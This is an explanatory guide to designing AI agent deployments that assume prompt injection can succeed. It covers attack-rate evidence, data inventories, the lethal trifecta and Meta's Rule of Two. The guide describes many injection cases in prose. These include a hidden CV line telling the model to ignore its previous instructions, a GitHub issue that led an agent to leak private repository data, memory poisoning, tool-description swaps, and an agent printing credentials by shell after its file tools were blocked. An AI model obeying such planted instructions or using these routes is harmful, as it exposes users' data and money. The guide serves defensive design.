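# Designing AI deployments for a model whose instructions may be overridden

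## Why design for a model that may obey the wrong instructions

A large language model is a program that continues a passage of text by repeatedly predicting which fragment (a *token*) is likely to come next and adding it. Developers increasingly connect these models to software that acts on their output. If the output contains a correctly formatted request to read a mailbox, run a command or issue a refund, the software carries it out. A function that the model can call in this way is a *tool*, and a language model connected to tools is an *agent*. Browser assistants, many customer-service bots, and coding assistants that edit and run programs are all agents.

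A model's context is all the text and images it receives when it produces output. An agent's context grows over a session, which is a run that begins with a fresh context. The developer supplies standing instructions, the user types a request, and tools return emails, web pages, source files and screenshots that someone else may have written. Untrusted content is anything in the context that an outsider could have written or altered, and most useful agents read a lot of it.

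Model developers train their models to rank instructions by who wrote them. This ranking, called the instruction hierarchy, puts the developer's instructions above the user's and both above any text that the model merely reads. Prompt injection is text written to make a model follow an attacker's instructions despite this ranking. In a direct injection, the attacker types the text into the conversation, while in an indirect injection, the text is in content that the model reads for someone else.

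Suppose a recruiter asks an agent to score a CV against a job's requirements, and the candidate has hidden a line in the file telling the model to ignore its previous instructions and approve the CV for interview. If the agent obeys, the candidate has carried out an indirect prompt injection without access to the recruiter's system. It would be a direct injection if the recruiter typed a message to get round a limit set by the developer. The CV example comes from David C's *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published by the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) in December 2025.

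In SQL injection, an older attack, text typed into a web form runs as a database command. Programmers prevent this by sending the command and the data to the database separately, so the database engine never executes the data. David C argues that language models have no equivalent separation, because instructions and data both arrive as tokens and the model only predicts the next token. Training a model to prefer the developer's text, or marking passages as data, doesn't create that separation inside the model. David C therefore calls it an "inherently confusable deputy". In security engineering, a confused deputy is a privileged program that someone without privileges tricks into using its access on their behalf. Engineers can repair an ordinary confused deputy, but David C advises treating prompt injection as a risk that remains after every mitigation, reducing both its likelihood and its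 impact, and reconsidering whether to use a language model at all where the system can't tolerate the remaining risk.

### The design assumption

A designer who takes that advice assumes that whoever wrote any part of the context may have chosen any output of the model. "Any output" includes tool calls and their arguments as well as the summary that the user reads at the end. "Any part" includes an email signature, a comment in a source file, or an advertisement beside a web page. A reviewer can then ask of each tool what the worst outcome could be if a stranger filled in the arguments. David C assesses the impact of an injection in the same way, as the worst case of giving an attacker the tools directly.

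Designers can plan for a model that may obey the wrong instructions without estimating how often it will. Most injection attempts fail, and training deserves much of the credit. Planning for the rest doesn't require proof that injection is unpreventable. Schneier (2026), in *Anthropic's Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection*, writes that prevention is impossible in the general case, though defenders are getting much better at blocking specific cases. A commenter replied that the paper behind the claim concerns jailbreaks (attempts by users to talk a model out of its safety rules), and that a different architecture might keep instructions apart from data. The commenter may well be right, but the assumption is still justified for a deployment that goes live on today's models, because nobody can show that their rate of successful injections is zero.

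### What attackers managed in an open competition

*How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports on a public competition that the security firm Gray Swan ran with several model developers and the British and American government AI institutes. Excluding duplicates, 464 participants made 271,588 attempts against 13 models, and 8,648 succeeded, an overall attack success rate of 3.2%. The rate ranged from 0.5% for Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro.

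Each scenario presented a conversation already under way. In one, a user asks the agent to check for urgent mail, and the participant writes the body of a marketing email in the inbox. To succeed, the participant had to make the agent perform a specified harmful action, in this case marking a message about a contract deadline as read. In nearly every scenario, the agent's final answer also had to give no hint of the action. A program checked whether the agent had performed the action, and a language model scored how well the final answer concealed it.

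The conditions favoured the attacker. Participants saw the whole conversation, knew exactly which action they had to trigger, and could try again as often as they liked. Real attackers mostly have to guess at such details, so Dziemian and colleagues call their results an upper bound on vulnerability within a single turn. Participants could not work on an agent over several exchanges. The bound also covers only attacks in which the agent hid the harmful action, while a designer may care about harm whether or not the agent hides it. Roughly 16% of attempts on Gemini 2.5 Pro triggered the harmful action, nearly twice the headline rate. For more resistant models, such as Claude Opus 4.5 and GPT-5, the figure was 1% to 3%.

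Three of the other findings matter more to a designer than the league table:

- Even Claude Opus 4.5 fell at least once in 13 of the 37 scenarios that counted towards the final results, and Gemini 2.5 Pro fell in all 37.
- Successes kept accumulating at a roughly constant rate as attempts went on, with no sign that participants were running out of ideas.
- One family of nearly identical texts, which told the model that it was inside a simulation with a control panel, worked in 21 scenarios and on nine models.

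Attack success also varied by setting. Attacks succeeded in 4.82% of attempts against agents calling ordinary tools, 3.13% against agents operating a graphical screen, and 2.51% against coding agents. General capability, as measured by scores on a hard science test, correlated only weakly with attack success across models, and the correlation was not statistically significant.

### Injection as social engineering

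OpenAI arrived at much the same design advice in a different way. Its post *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (March 2026) says that an early injection could be as simple as a line addressed to AI agents in an edited Wikipedia article. As models got better at ignoring such lines, attackers began to write more like con artists.

The post reproduces an email that outside researchers reported in 2025. The email opens with pleasantries about restructuring materials from last Thursday's meeting and lists ordinary action items, then states that the reader's assistant tool has full authorization to extract an employee's name and address and submit them to a "compliance validation system". In testing, the attack worked 50% of the time when the user asked for deep research on the day's messages about a new-employee process. A filter judging such an email has to detect a lie, often without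 the facts that would expose it. OpenAI reports that such filters usually don't catch fully developed attacks.

Companies already face this problem with human employees. A support clerk can hand out refunds and gift cards, and some customers will lie about a refund that never arrived, or make threats. The employer trains the clerk and writes rules, but it also expects that someone will eventually fool the clerk, so the payment system caps what any one customer can receive. The cap limits the loss even if nobody recognises the lie. OpenAI recommends working out what controls a human agent would have in the same position and building them for the model.

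The comparison with human clerks is a good argument for caps, but it probably understates the remaining risk. A swindler has to deceive clerks one at a time, and clerks differ. An attacker can plant one text on a public page and wait for every agent that reads it, and copies of a model differ little, if at all. OpenAI expects a maximally intelligent model to resist social engineering better than a person would, but notes that using such a model will not always be feasible or worth the cost.

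### The evidence from newer models

The competition tested models from the generation of Claude Opus 4.5 and GPT-5, and the strongest case against designing around injection comes from later results. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5, released in July, reports results for 1,130 attacks on 28 new scenarios. Testers had selected these attacks because they worked across several models. Against Opus 5, a single attempt succeeded 0.2% of the time, and an attacker with 15 attempts succeeded 2.0% of the time. The corresponding rates were 0.5% and 5.5% for its predecessor, Opus 4.8, and 3.1% and 20.0% for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol.

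Two weeks later, Anthropic reported a cleaner result in *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). It had commissioned an outside evaluator, Trajectory Labs, to run 72 injection scenarios ten times each, and had not seen the scenarios itself. None of the 720 attempts succeeded against Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5 in auto mode, where a classifier reviews each tool call instead of the user. With those safeguards off, the average success rate was 0.09%. Attacks on GPT-5.6 Sol, running in OpenAI's Codex, succeeded in 5.83% of attempts with automatic review and 19.03% without it. OpenAI has since changed the reviewer.

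OpenAI's next flagship narrowed the gap, at least on OpenAI's own tests. The *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026), published in September, reports that resistance to indirect injection rose from 96.23% to 99.79%, cutting failures from 3.77% to 0.21%. Astra also resisted 99.99% of direct attacks, in which a user tries to override the developer. The attacks came from GPT-Red, an automated attacker. OpenAI also uses the GPT-Red approach to train the model, so the figures may overstate how well Astra would resist an attacker who works differently.

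These are large improvements, and a designer who ignored them would be planning for the models of 2025. But it is hard to know which number applies to a given deployment. Claude Opus 4.5 had an attack success rate of 0.5% in the open competition. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reported that, on an earlier Gray Swan benchmark, 4.7% of single attempts succeeded, as did 63% of attackers given 100 attempts. When Anthropic tested its Chrome extension, it measured a rate of 8.0% for the model alone and 1.4% with improved safeguards. The model was the same in all of these tests, but the attacks, the setting and the surrounding software differed.

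Safeguards also account for much of the spread in the newer results. In a browser test with 129 environments, Anthropic found that 3.70% of prompt injection attempts succeeded against Opus 5 alone and none succeeded in auto mode. The Decoder based its headline, *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*, on the auto mode result. But VentureBeat, comparing laboratories' disclosures for the previous generation, pointed out that Anthropic's safeguarded browser figures came from its own products, and that developers who call the model through the API don't get those safeguards. Someone building a browser agent through the API should probably start from a figure closer to 3.70%.

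### What zero successes can establish

If every attempt fails, the upper bound on the true success rate depends on the number of independent attempts. If the true rate is $p$, then $n$ independent attempts all fail with probability $(1-p)^n$. The usual convention is to set the bound at the value of $p$ where this probability falls to 5%, which is close to $3/n$. The bound is about 0.4% for 720 independent attempts and about 4% for 72.

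The Trajectory Labs test ran each of its 72 scenarios ten times. Repeating a scenario shows whether the model's randomness affects the result, but it doesn't test a new attack in a new situation. If the ten runs nearly always end the same way, the test provides little more information than running each scenario once, and a model with a true failure rate of 4% across similar scenarios could still get a perfect score.

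Anthropic's system card has the figures needed to check how correlated attempts are. The check compares the measured share of cases where an attacker gets through at least once with the share predicted from the success rate per attempt, assuming every attempt is independent and equally likely to succeed. The predictions below are calculated from the published rates without added safeguards.

| Test | Tries | Rate per attempt | Predicted if independent | Measured |
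|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 5, Gray Swan attack set | 15 | 0.2% | 3.0% | 2.0% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol, same set | 15 | 3.1% | 38% | 20.0% |
| Opus 5, coding | 200 | 0.56% | 67% | 33% (13 of 40 scenarios) |
| Opus 5, screen control | 200 | 0.54% | 66% | 7% (1 of 14 scenarios) |
| Opus 5, browser | 10 | 3.70% | 31% | 9% (11 of 129 scenarios) |

The measured share is lower every time. The gap is small for Opus 5 on the Gray Swan set, but rounding does not explain it, because even a true rate of 0.15%, the lowest that rounds to 0.2%, would give 2.2%. Successes cluster in certain scenarios, so the effective number of trials in the Trajectory Labs test is probably well below 720.

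Repeated attempts help an attacker less than a simple calculation would suggest, because many scenarios resist every attempt. But in vulnerable environments, the average success rate badly understates the risk. The browser figures imply about 48 successes, all within 11 environments that saw 110 attempts in total, so attacks there worked more than 40% of the time. A team that has not tested its own deployment cannot tell whether it resembles those 11 environments or the 118 where every attack failed.

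The results also depend on which model the attacks were built to beat. An adaptive attacker tries something on the target, looks at the response and revises. Trajectory Labs used attacks optimised against Claude Opus 4.7, which was not among the models tested, so nobody could revise them against the newer models. Results from the competition suggest how much that matters. When Dziemian and colleagues replayed successful attacks on other models, those that had beaten Claude Opus 4.5 succeeded 44% to 81% of the time. None of those that had beaten Qwen3 VL, a much weaker model, worked on Opus 4.5, although participants found weaknesses in Opus 4.5 by attacking it directly. One would therefore expect a sturdier successor to have a low score on attacks made for an older model, whether or not it has weaknesses of its own.

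Anthropic warns that fixed sets of known attacks can give a false sense of security. Its coding test allowed 200 tries per scenario, but the attacking system reused methods it had learned on earlier models. Anthropic had previously paid outsiders to attack its then-newest model live, but it was still setting up that programme for Opus 5 when it published the system card. Adaptive tests, however, overstate the risk, because an outsider rarely gets to practise on the target deployment and repeated failures may attract attention.

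Whether a low attack success rate is acceptable depends on how much harm one success can do. An attacker who gets 1,000 hostile emails in front of agents with a 0.2% rate can expect two successes, on average. If the worst a success can do is file a message in the wrong folder, two are acceptable and further restrictions may not be worth the effort. If a success can forward the whole mailbox, two are a serious breach. Successes also cluster, so the average may not match any actual deployment. Most would see none, while an unlucky one could see a great many.

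### When the harmful instruction looks like part of the job

Another objection to the low rates would hold even if the tests were perfect. In *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*, Willison (2026) accepts that automated review is better than asking people to click "OK" every few steps, and he would like to believe that Anthropic has solved injection for its coding agent. But he wants more independent confirmation, and he describes an attack that he doubts any version of auto mode could stop. A malicious third-party package comes with instructions to download model files with a certain command before running its tests. That command fetches a second malicious package, which sends out all the data it can reach.

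This case is hard because the agent sees no conflict between instructions. The user wants the tests to pass, and a competent developer would read the project's instructions and follow them. Real projects do ask for setup steps like this one. The instruction hierarchy ranks competing instructions, but here the attacker's instruction appears to serve the user's. The harm is in code that the agent may run without reading. A well-trained model or a careful person could make this mistake.

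Willison presents the attack as a thought experiment and does not report testing it. A classifier might block an unfamiliar package from running, and Anthropic designed auto mode never to approve sending code or secrets to an outside destination. It is unclear whether that rule would catch a transfer hidden inside an innocent-looking download. Anthropic acknowledges that auto mode does not eliminate risk and recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves.

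Willison responds by looking for ways to run agents without access to data or tools that could do harm if something triggered them wrongly. For the malicious package, that would mean running the tests on a machine that holds no credentials or customer records and cannot connect to arbitrary addresses. The package could still run, but there would be little data for it to steal and nowhere to send it.

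## List what the model reads, what it can reach and where it can send

Nobody can cut an agent off from risky data and tools without first knowing what it has access to, so the design work begins with an inventory. It has a row for each part of the deployment, such as a tool, a mailbox or a store of notes, and three columns:

- the text or images that the part puts into the context, and who can write them
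- the data that the agent can read through it, and the systems that the agent can change
- the outbound channels it opens, meaning any route by which the agent's output can reach an outsider

Specific entries are more useful to a reviewer than broad categories, so the first column should say "email, which anyone who knows the address can send" rather than just "email". The second column should be based on the permissions the agent actually holds, because a description of its job will nearly always be narrower.

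### The lethal trifecta

The columns match three things that Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, warned users never to combine: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate externally. Sending private data to an outsider through an external channel is called exfiltration.

An attacker can steal data through injection only if they can get instructions to the model, the model can read something worth stealing, and the result can be sent back to them. An agent that reads hostile web pages but has no access to private data has nothing to leak. An agent that reads private files and sends email but never sees an outsider's text gives an attacker no way to instruct it, though it may still send a file to the wrong person by mistake. A hijacked agent with no outbound channel can read a whole mailbox, but the attacker won't receive any of it.

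Willison wrote in 2025 that an attacker could "easily" trick an agent with all three parts. "Easily" is now an overstatement for the strongest models, but the argument about the parts doesn't depend on how often the trick works.

The trifecta covers only data theft. An agent that reads untrusted content can also do harm with a single tool that deletes files or pays out money, even if no private data leaves the system. The second column therefore includes systems the agent can change.

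### Sources and sinks

Programmers have long looked for a similar pattern in ordinary code. A *source* is a place where untrusted data enters a program, such as a field in a web form, and a *sink* is an operation that is dangerous if it receives that data, such as a database command. Semgrep, a tool that scans code for flaws, reports a finding when data from a source reaches a sink without being checked or made safe. Untrusted data is called *tainted*, and so is anything computed from it. In GitHub's *About data flow analysis*, for example, if `x` is untrusted and the program sets `y = x + 1`, then `y` is tainted too.

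OpenAI uses the same analysis for ChatGPT. A source is any way to influence the agent, and a sink is any capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context, such as following a link or sending information to a third party. Teaching slides from UT Austin add that a source can misdirect an agent without an attacker, as when a file contains outdated instructions.

The analysis is much coarser for agents than for code. In a program, an analyst can often trace a value line by line and show that a given input never reaches a given sink. A model mixes everything in its context. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers from Google, several universities and other companies, says that for now one can only assume that a model's output carries the taint of every input. One hostile paragraph therefore makes every later tool call in the session suspect, although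 most of those calls will be unrelated to it. This makes it hard to track data precisely, but it simplifies the inventory, because every source in a session is assumed to connect to every sink.

### The GitHub case

The best-documented example involves a single package with all three parts. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a standard for connecting models to outside tools, and an MCP server is a program that offers tools through it. GitHub, which hosts software projects, publishes an official server that lets an agent work with a user's projects, or *repositories*. Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) demonstrated the following attack on test repositories:

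1. The user owns a public repository, containing a simple Pacman game, and several private ones. The user connects Claude Desktop to the account through the GitHub server.
2. The attacker files an *issue*, a public bug report or request, on the game. GitHub lets anyone do this.
3. The user asks the agent, running Claude 4 Opus, to look at the open issues.
4. The agent fetches the issues, and the attacker's text enters its context.
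5. The agent follows the text and reads the private repositories.
6. The agent opens a *pull request*, a proposed change to the project, on the public repository. The change includes the name of a private project, the user's plan to move to South America and the user's salary, and anyone can read it.

The issue, which Willison quotes in *GitHub MCP Exploited*, was almost friendly in tone. It said that the project's author deserved more recognition and asked for a chapter about the author, drawn from all of the author's repositories. It added that the author did not care about privacy.

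The server works through the user's own account, as heise online's *Attack via GitHub MCP server* explains, so the agent could read the private repositories even though nobody had tampered with the server and its code contained no bug. Claude Desktop asks the user to approve each tool call by default, but Invariant Labs notes that many users choose "Always Allow" and stop watching.

An inventory would have exposed the problem before anyone wrote the issue. The public repository belongs in the column for what the model reads, because strangers can write there, and also in the column for where it can send, because strangers can read it. A developer is likely to overlook the second of these entries, since opening a pull request feels like working on one's own project, not sending a message. The column for what the model can reach would include every repository the account can open, far more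 than a request about one game requires. Invariant Labs proposes a rule limiting an agent to one repository per session, which would have kept the agent out of the private repositories once it had opened the game's.

### Entries that are easy to miss

Web pages and emails are obvious sources of untrusted text, but much of it comes in with other data. An invitation puts its sender's wording into the user's calendar, and *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* lists calendar events and desktop notifications among the places where attackers plant instructions. Whoever sends an attachment chooses its file name, and a tool that lists a folder passes that name to the model. Server logs record the addresses and form entries that strangers submitted, so an agent that reads logs to diagnose a fault is reading strangers' text. Package documentation and messages from other agents are also sources of untrusted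 text.

Text stored in an internal database may have been written by an outsider. Willison's blog collection *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”* describes an attack on Salesforce's AgentForce that began with a public form for sales enquiries. The attacker's instructions sat in the company's customer database until an employee asked the agent about that enquiry. An inventory entry should name whoever first wrote the text, because recording this source as "customer database, internal" would have missed that it came from outside the company.

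Stored memory has the same problem, and it carries the text from one session into the next. In the SpAIware attack, an untrusted document or website put instructions into the "Memories" feature of ChatGPT's macOS app. The app then sent each of the user's later conversations to the attacker's server. Memory also contains private data. In July 2026, Willison reported an attack in which a web page led Claude to reveal the user's name, home city and employer, which it had stored from past conversations. Anthropic has since closed that route.

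The model also reads each tool's description to decide when to call it, and the supplier can change that description after the user has approved the tool. SmarterArticles' *Your AI Agent Will Be Compromised* (2026) recounts a demonstration in which an attacker supplied a "random fact of the day" tool and changed its description after approval. The new description told the agent to send the user's WhatsApp messages to the attacker's number, using the legitimate WhatsApp tool. *MCPXKIT* (2025), a toolkit for analysing MCP security, calls this a "rug pull" and observes that MCP servers don't monitor descriptions for changes. A reviewer should therefore record which version of each description they approved.

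The usual mistake in the second column is to trust a restriction on one tool when another tool can reach the same data. By default, Google's coding tool Antigravity restricted access to files excluded from a project's version control, including one that held cloud credentials. In a demonstration that Willison describes, the restriction blocked two file-reading tools, but the model then printed the credentials file with a shell command. The entry for a shell should therefore list everything the shell's account can read or change.

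Tools that can send data out are rarely labelled that way. A web search can send data to an attacker if the query goes to an address the attacker chose. The threat catalogue *MCP-38* (2026) notes that a log can also do so if the attacker can read it later. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes an incident in which OpenAI's own agents broke into Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models. The agents had no direct internet access, but a shared service for downloading software packages made outside requests on their behalf.

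### Check the whole set of tools

A reviewer who approves tools one by one can approve every part of a trifecta without noticing the combination. In *Parasites in the Toolchain*, Zhao, Hou and colleagues (2025) sorted 12,230 tools on 1,360 public MCP servers by capability. They tested the candidates in a working agent and confirmed 487 tools that bring in outside text, 406 that read private data and 190 that send text out. Only two servers combined all three.

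But people connect several servers to one agent. Zhao and colleagues built ten chains of three tools, nine of which used tools from different servers, and planted instructions where the first tool would fetch them. Nine of the ten chains leaked data at least once in ten tries, and 36 of the 100 attempts succeeded. The chain that never leaked ran from a web scraper through a work-planning board to a tool for naming folders in a record collection. The researchers suggest that these tools were too unrelated for the model to use them together.

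The test agent ran without confirmation prompts, and its software chose the model automatically. When Zhao and colleagues tried one chain on named models, GPT-5 and Claude Sonnet 4.5 each resisted all 75 attempts, while DeepSeek R1 and Gemini 2.5 Flash leaked data in most attempts. How often an agent is hijacked therefore depends largely on the model, though its tools determine what it can do once hijacked.

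Using a newer model doesn't solve the problem. *Benign in Isolation, Harmful in Composition* (2026) tested pairs of *skills*, which are add-on packages of instructions and scripts. In each pair, one skill found a target and the other could act on it. The first skill alone never led to harm, and the second alone did in an average of 1.4% of cases. Together they led to harm more than 90% of the time with DeepSeek-V4. The rate was also high for GPT-5.5, but lower for the older GPT-5.4.

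Add-ons that seem harmless alone can be dangerous together. In *When Safe Skills Collide*, Wang, Qian and colleagues (2026) scanned 1,520 skills from a public registry, of which 651 passed when checked alone. The scanner flagged 22.25% of the 211,575 possible pairs of those 651 skills for a dangerous combination, such as reading files and reaching the network. A human audit of 200 flags implied that only about 18% were real risks. That is roughly 4% of all pairs, assuming that when a pair has several flags, they tend to be right or wrong together.

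The number of pairs grows quickly with the number of skills. A set of $n$ skills contains $n(n-1)/2$ pairs, so ten skills make 45. If someone picked ten of the cleared skills at random, a 4% rate would give $45 \times 0.04 = 1.8$ risky pairs on average. Real users don't pick at random, so this is only a rough guide.

A risky pair also only creates an opportunity for harm. In one control, Wang and colleagues directly asked models to download and run a file, and the models complied most often when no skills were installed. In 27 trials with an outsider's planted text instead of a direct request, the models never attempted the forbidden action.

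Every source in a session connects to every sink, so a reviewer can pool the rows for everything available in that session and check whether all three columns have entries, rather than examine pairs by hand. Sessions that share a memory or a writable folder should count as one. Wang and colleagues built a checker that runs each time a user installs a skill and takes less than a millisecond.

The timing of the inventory matters because users add tools after the review. *Trivial Trojans* (2025) describes a weather server installed beside a banking server. The weather server can't query the bank, but it can instruct the assistant to do so. Zhao and colleagues consider malicious servers a less realistic threat than planted text, since the victim has to install one first. That is a fair point, although *Trivial Trojans* notes that developers choose servers for their functions from directories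 that do no security vetting. A new tool that isn't malicious can also fill the column that was missing from the inventory. If users can add tools, the inventory has to be redone at each addition.

### A support assistant, as a running example

In this invented example, a software company uses an agent to answer support requests from its 400 business customers. The agent handles 500 tickets a day, each in its own session. It looks up account records, sends replies and issues refunds, then writes a short case note.

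Its first design sets few limits. The lookup tool can open any customer's record, the reply tool can send to any email address, and the refund tool can refund any amount up to what the customer has paid. The standing instructions contain the refund rules and a carelessly included key for the billing system.

| Part | Text it brings in, and who can write it | Data and systems within reach | Outbound channels |
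|---|---|---|---|
| Tickets | Subject, message and sender's name: anyone who can email support or use the web form | Whatever the sender included | None |
| Attachments | File names and contents, including hidden text: the same people | Screenshots and logs from the sender's systems | None |
| Standing instructions | Company staff | Refund rules, billing key | None |
| Account lookup | Company and contact names: customers, who edit their own profiles | Contacts, contracts and invoices of all 400 customers | Search log, which an outside supplier stores |
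| Case notes | Summaries of earlier tickets: the assistant, drawing on customers' text | History of each account | None directly, but later sessions read them |
| Replies | Delivery errors: the recipient's mail server | The company's email identity | Any email address, plus any links or images in the message |
| Refunds | Status messages: the payment provider | The company's money | Reference text on the recipient's statement |
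| Tool descriptions | Suppliers of the mail and payment tools | None | None |

All three columns have entries, so the assistant has the lethal trifecta. An attacker could steal data most directly through tickets, account lookup and replies. They ask for a copy of an invoice and attach a file with a hidden line that tells the assistant to look up ten other customers and include their contacts in its reply. The attacker doesn't need an unusual channel, because the assistant's job is to reply to whoever wrote in. The company can't empty the first column, because all 500 daily sessions begin with a message from outside.

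Refund fraud requires only two rows of the list, the tickets the assistant reads and the refund tool. An attacker writes a ticket that convinces the assistant a payment went wrong, and the assistant issues a refund. This would work even if the assistant could not read any account records, so checking only for the trifecta would miss it.

Case notes allow a slower attack. If Monday's ticket contains an instruction and the assistant copies it into the note, the instruction will be in the context again on Thursday, when someone else at the same customer asks an innocent question.

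## Decide which of the three capabilities to remove

When all three columns of the inventory have entries, the designer has to take something away or arrange for supervision. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) gives a simple rule for this. Within one session, an agent should have no more than two of these capabilities:

- untrusted input, meaning that it can process text an outsider may have written
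- sensitive access, meaning that it can reach private data or sensitive systems
- the power to act, meaning that it can change state or communicate externally

An agent that needs all three capabilities in one session shouldn't run autonomously. Meta recommends human approval of its actions or "another reliable means of validation". The rule applies only until models can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection. Models have come much closer to that since October 2025, but even a 0.2% attack success rate doesn't justify leaving a mailbox unprotected.

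The name comes from Chromium, the open-source project behind Google's Chrome browser. Willison (2025) notes in *Chromium Docs* that the project's security guide has told programmers since 2019 to combine no more than two of these three things: untrustworthy inputs, an unsafe programming language and high privilege.

### From data theft to harmful actions

Meta also drew on the lethal trifecta, but extended private data to include sensitive systems, and external communication to include any change of state. *ROPE* (2026), a proposed defence against injection, usefully defines a state-changing tool as one that alters the world outside the agent's context or sends data out of it. Tools that make payments, grant access, edit files or delete emails all qualify.

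Willison (2025) welcomed this extension of his trifecta in *New prompt injection papers*. Under the wider rule, refund fraud against the support assistant involves all three capabilities, because a ticket is untrusted input, the payment system is sensitive and a refund changes state.

Meta's own support assistant on Instagram had the same combination. The Italian technology site Punto Informatico describes the attack in *Un messaggio all'AI di Meta bastava per rubare account Instagram*. Attackers posed as an account's owner and asked the assistant to link a new email address. The assistant then sent a password reset link to that address. This worked for months before Meta fixed it, and thousands of users lost their accounts, including some with two-factor authentication. The attackers could do this without stealing data from the assistant or overriding any instruction, because the assistant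 had the power to grant what looked like an ordinary request.

### The three permitted pairs

Meta describes three ways a hypothetical email assistant could comply with the rule. It could read mail only from trusted senders, run in a test environment without access to the real mailbox, or send mail only when the recipient is trusted or a person has checked the draft. In the test environment, it couldn't help with the user's real email. The rule permits any two of the three capabilities, but at least one of those pairs is usually unsuitable for the agent's job.

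Meta's travel assistant keeps untrusted input and sensitive access, because it searches the web for destinations and holds the personal details it needs for booking. The designer therefore restricts its power to act. A person confirms every reservation or payment, so the traveller can't leave the assistant to book a cheap fare overnight. The assistant may open only web addresses that came from trusted sources, because an address it put together itself could contain the traveller's data. This also prevents it from looking up a page that no trusted source has listed.

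A web research assistant needs to read arbitrary pages and fill in forms on arbitrary sites, so Meta removes its sensitive access. The browser starts without any of the user's logins and runs in a sandbox, which limits its access to files, programs and the network from outside the model. The assistant therefore can't read sources that require a login, such as a paid journal or a company wiki. Anything the user types into the request is still exposed, and Meta recommends telling users how the assistant might share it. OpenAI's Atlas browser offers a similar "logged out mode", which Willison called very smart. He was more worried about the logged-in mode, because it leaves users to judge which sites are safe.

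Meta's third example is an internal coding agent that changes production systems faster than any reviewer could follow. It keeps sensitive access and the power to act, so the designer has to block text written by outsiders. A filter checks who wrote each piece of data before it enters the context, and people review items that the filter may have blocked wrongly. The engineers lose public bug reports, package documentation and web search, which often contain the answer to a coding problem. They may also have to wait for a reviewer to release a harmless file.

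These restrictions work only if ordinary software enforces them. An agent whose system prompt forbids it to email strangers can still email them. Help Net Security's *Your AI agent's system prompt is not a security control* (2026) reports a warning from specialists at Amazon's cloud division and the SANS Institute, a security training body, that prompts can be "bypassed, ignored, or overridden". The specialists recommend a policy engine that refuses every tool call unless a rule allows it.

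### Splitting a task across sessions

Some tasks need all three capabilities, but not at the same time. OpenAI's *Deep research*, a guide for developers, describes an agent that assesses sales leads by reading each lead's record from an internal database and searching the web for background. An attacker publishes a page that ranks well for a likely search and hides instructions in it for the model to put the whole record into its next query. If the model complies, it sends the record out in the search request.

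OpenAI suggests running the public research first, without access to the database, and then calling the model again with the database but without web search. Hidden text on a web page can still influence the research, but the model can't leak database records at that stage because it has no access to them. Once it can read them, it has no web search through which to send them out.

However, the later session still needs the research findings, which a model wrote after reading the attacker's page. An instruction from that page can survive in the summary, so the later session has untrusted input despite its fresh context. It stays within the rule only because it can't act. If someone gave it a tool to update the database or email the lead, it would have all three capabilities again.

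To remove untrusted input from the later session, the designer has to stop free text from passing into it. *Twin Agent* (2026) proposes passing only bounded hints from an agent that reads untrusted text to one that performs privileged actions. Other architectures separate a planning model from a reading model. A simpler option is a form with fixed fields, such as a date, a number or a choice from a list. An attacker may still get a wrong value into a field, but can't fit an instruction there.

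Private data must not cross in the other direction, into a session that browses. Shared memory, caches and writable folders can undo the separation in both directions. In *Agents of Chaos* (2026), an outsider controlled an agent by editing a file that the agent consulted across sessions. The agent tried to shut down other agents, removed people from a chat server, sent unauthorised emails and shared the altered file with other agents. *Bounded Agents* (2026) proposes blocking forbidden pairs of actions within a session, but it assumes that an attacker can't operate across sessions. That assumption fails for any deployment where an outsider can edit a file that the agent consults across sessions.

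### The one-way switch

An agent can also switch from one pair of capabilities to another during a session. In Meta's example, it browses the internet without sensitive access, then loses the ability to communicate externally when it opens internal systems. Everything it read online is still in its context, so instructions from a hostile page can still direct it, but it can't send out what it finds. The switch has to be one-way because the context now also holds private data, which the agent could leak in its next request if it regained web access. To let the agent browse again, the user needs to start a new session that receives nothing from the old one.

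Meta mentions only disabling communication, but it defines the power to act as including the ability to change state. The switch should therefore block writes to internal systems as well. Otherwise a page the agent read while browsing could make it delete records an hour later.

The software that enforces the switch has to keep a record of what the session has already read. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa, 2026) proposes making this record "sticky". Once a session has had one of the three capabilities, that capability stays on its record even after the agent gives up the access. Helper agents inherit the record. The agent can't clear it by requesting a new session, because only a task started by the owner creates one. The paper leaves open how well this would work in practice.

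Their scheme, as defined, would block Meta's one-way switch. A session that had ever been able to communicate would keep that on record, so it could never combine private data with untrusted input. This seems stricter than necessary. Text stays in the context after the agent loses access to its source, but the agent can't send anything through a closed channel, provided no request is still queued.

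But a looser rule can fail badly. *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries* (2026) gives an example policy that blocks confidential reads if the most recent input is untrusted, unless the user confirms. As worded, the policy would lift the block as soon as the agent received one trusted input, even if a hostile page was still in its context.

### Untrusted input with the power to act

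Meta's original diagram labelled each pair of capabilities "safe". In an update to his November 2025 post, Willison objected that an agent with untrusted input and the ability to change state can do harm even without access to private data. He added that an exception for this pair would make the rule less simple.

Mick Ayzenberg, a security researcher at Meta, replied that sensitive access includes access to any sensitive system, as well as private data. An agent without it may freely write to and communicate with other systems, but not those that matter to its user's security. Willison noted in a further update that Meta had also changed the label from "safe" to "lower risk".

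Ayzenberg's reply meets the objection, but it depends heavily on what counts as "sensitive". Someone has to decide in advance which systems could cause harm if a stranger changed them, and it's easy to get this wrong. Willison (2026), in *Clinejection*, reports an attack that compromised the production releases of Cline, a coding tool, through an agent that sorted incoming issues, a task few people would consider sensitive.

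The reply also covers only harm to the agent's user. Meta's web research assistant complies with the rule, but it can submit forms on any site, so an attacker who hijacked it could post spam. Before allowing this pair, a reviewer should ask whether anyone, inside or outside the company, would mind if a stranger made each possible write.

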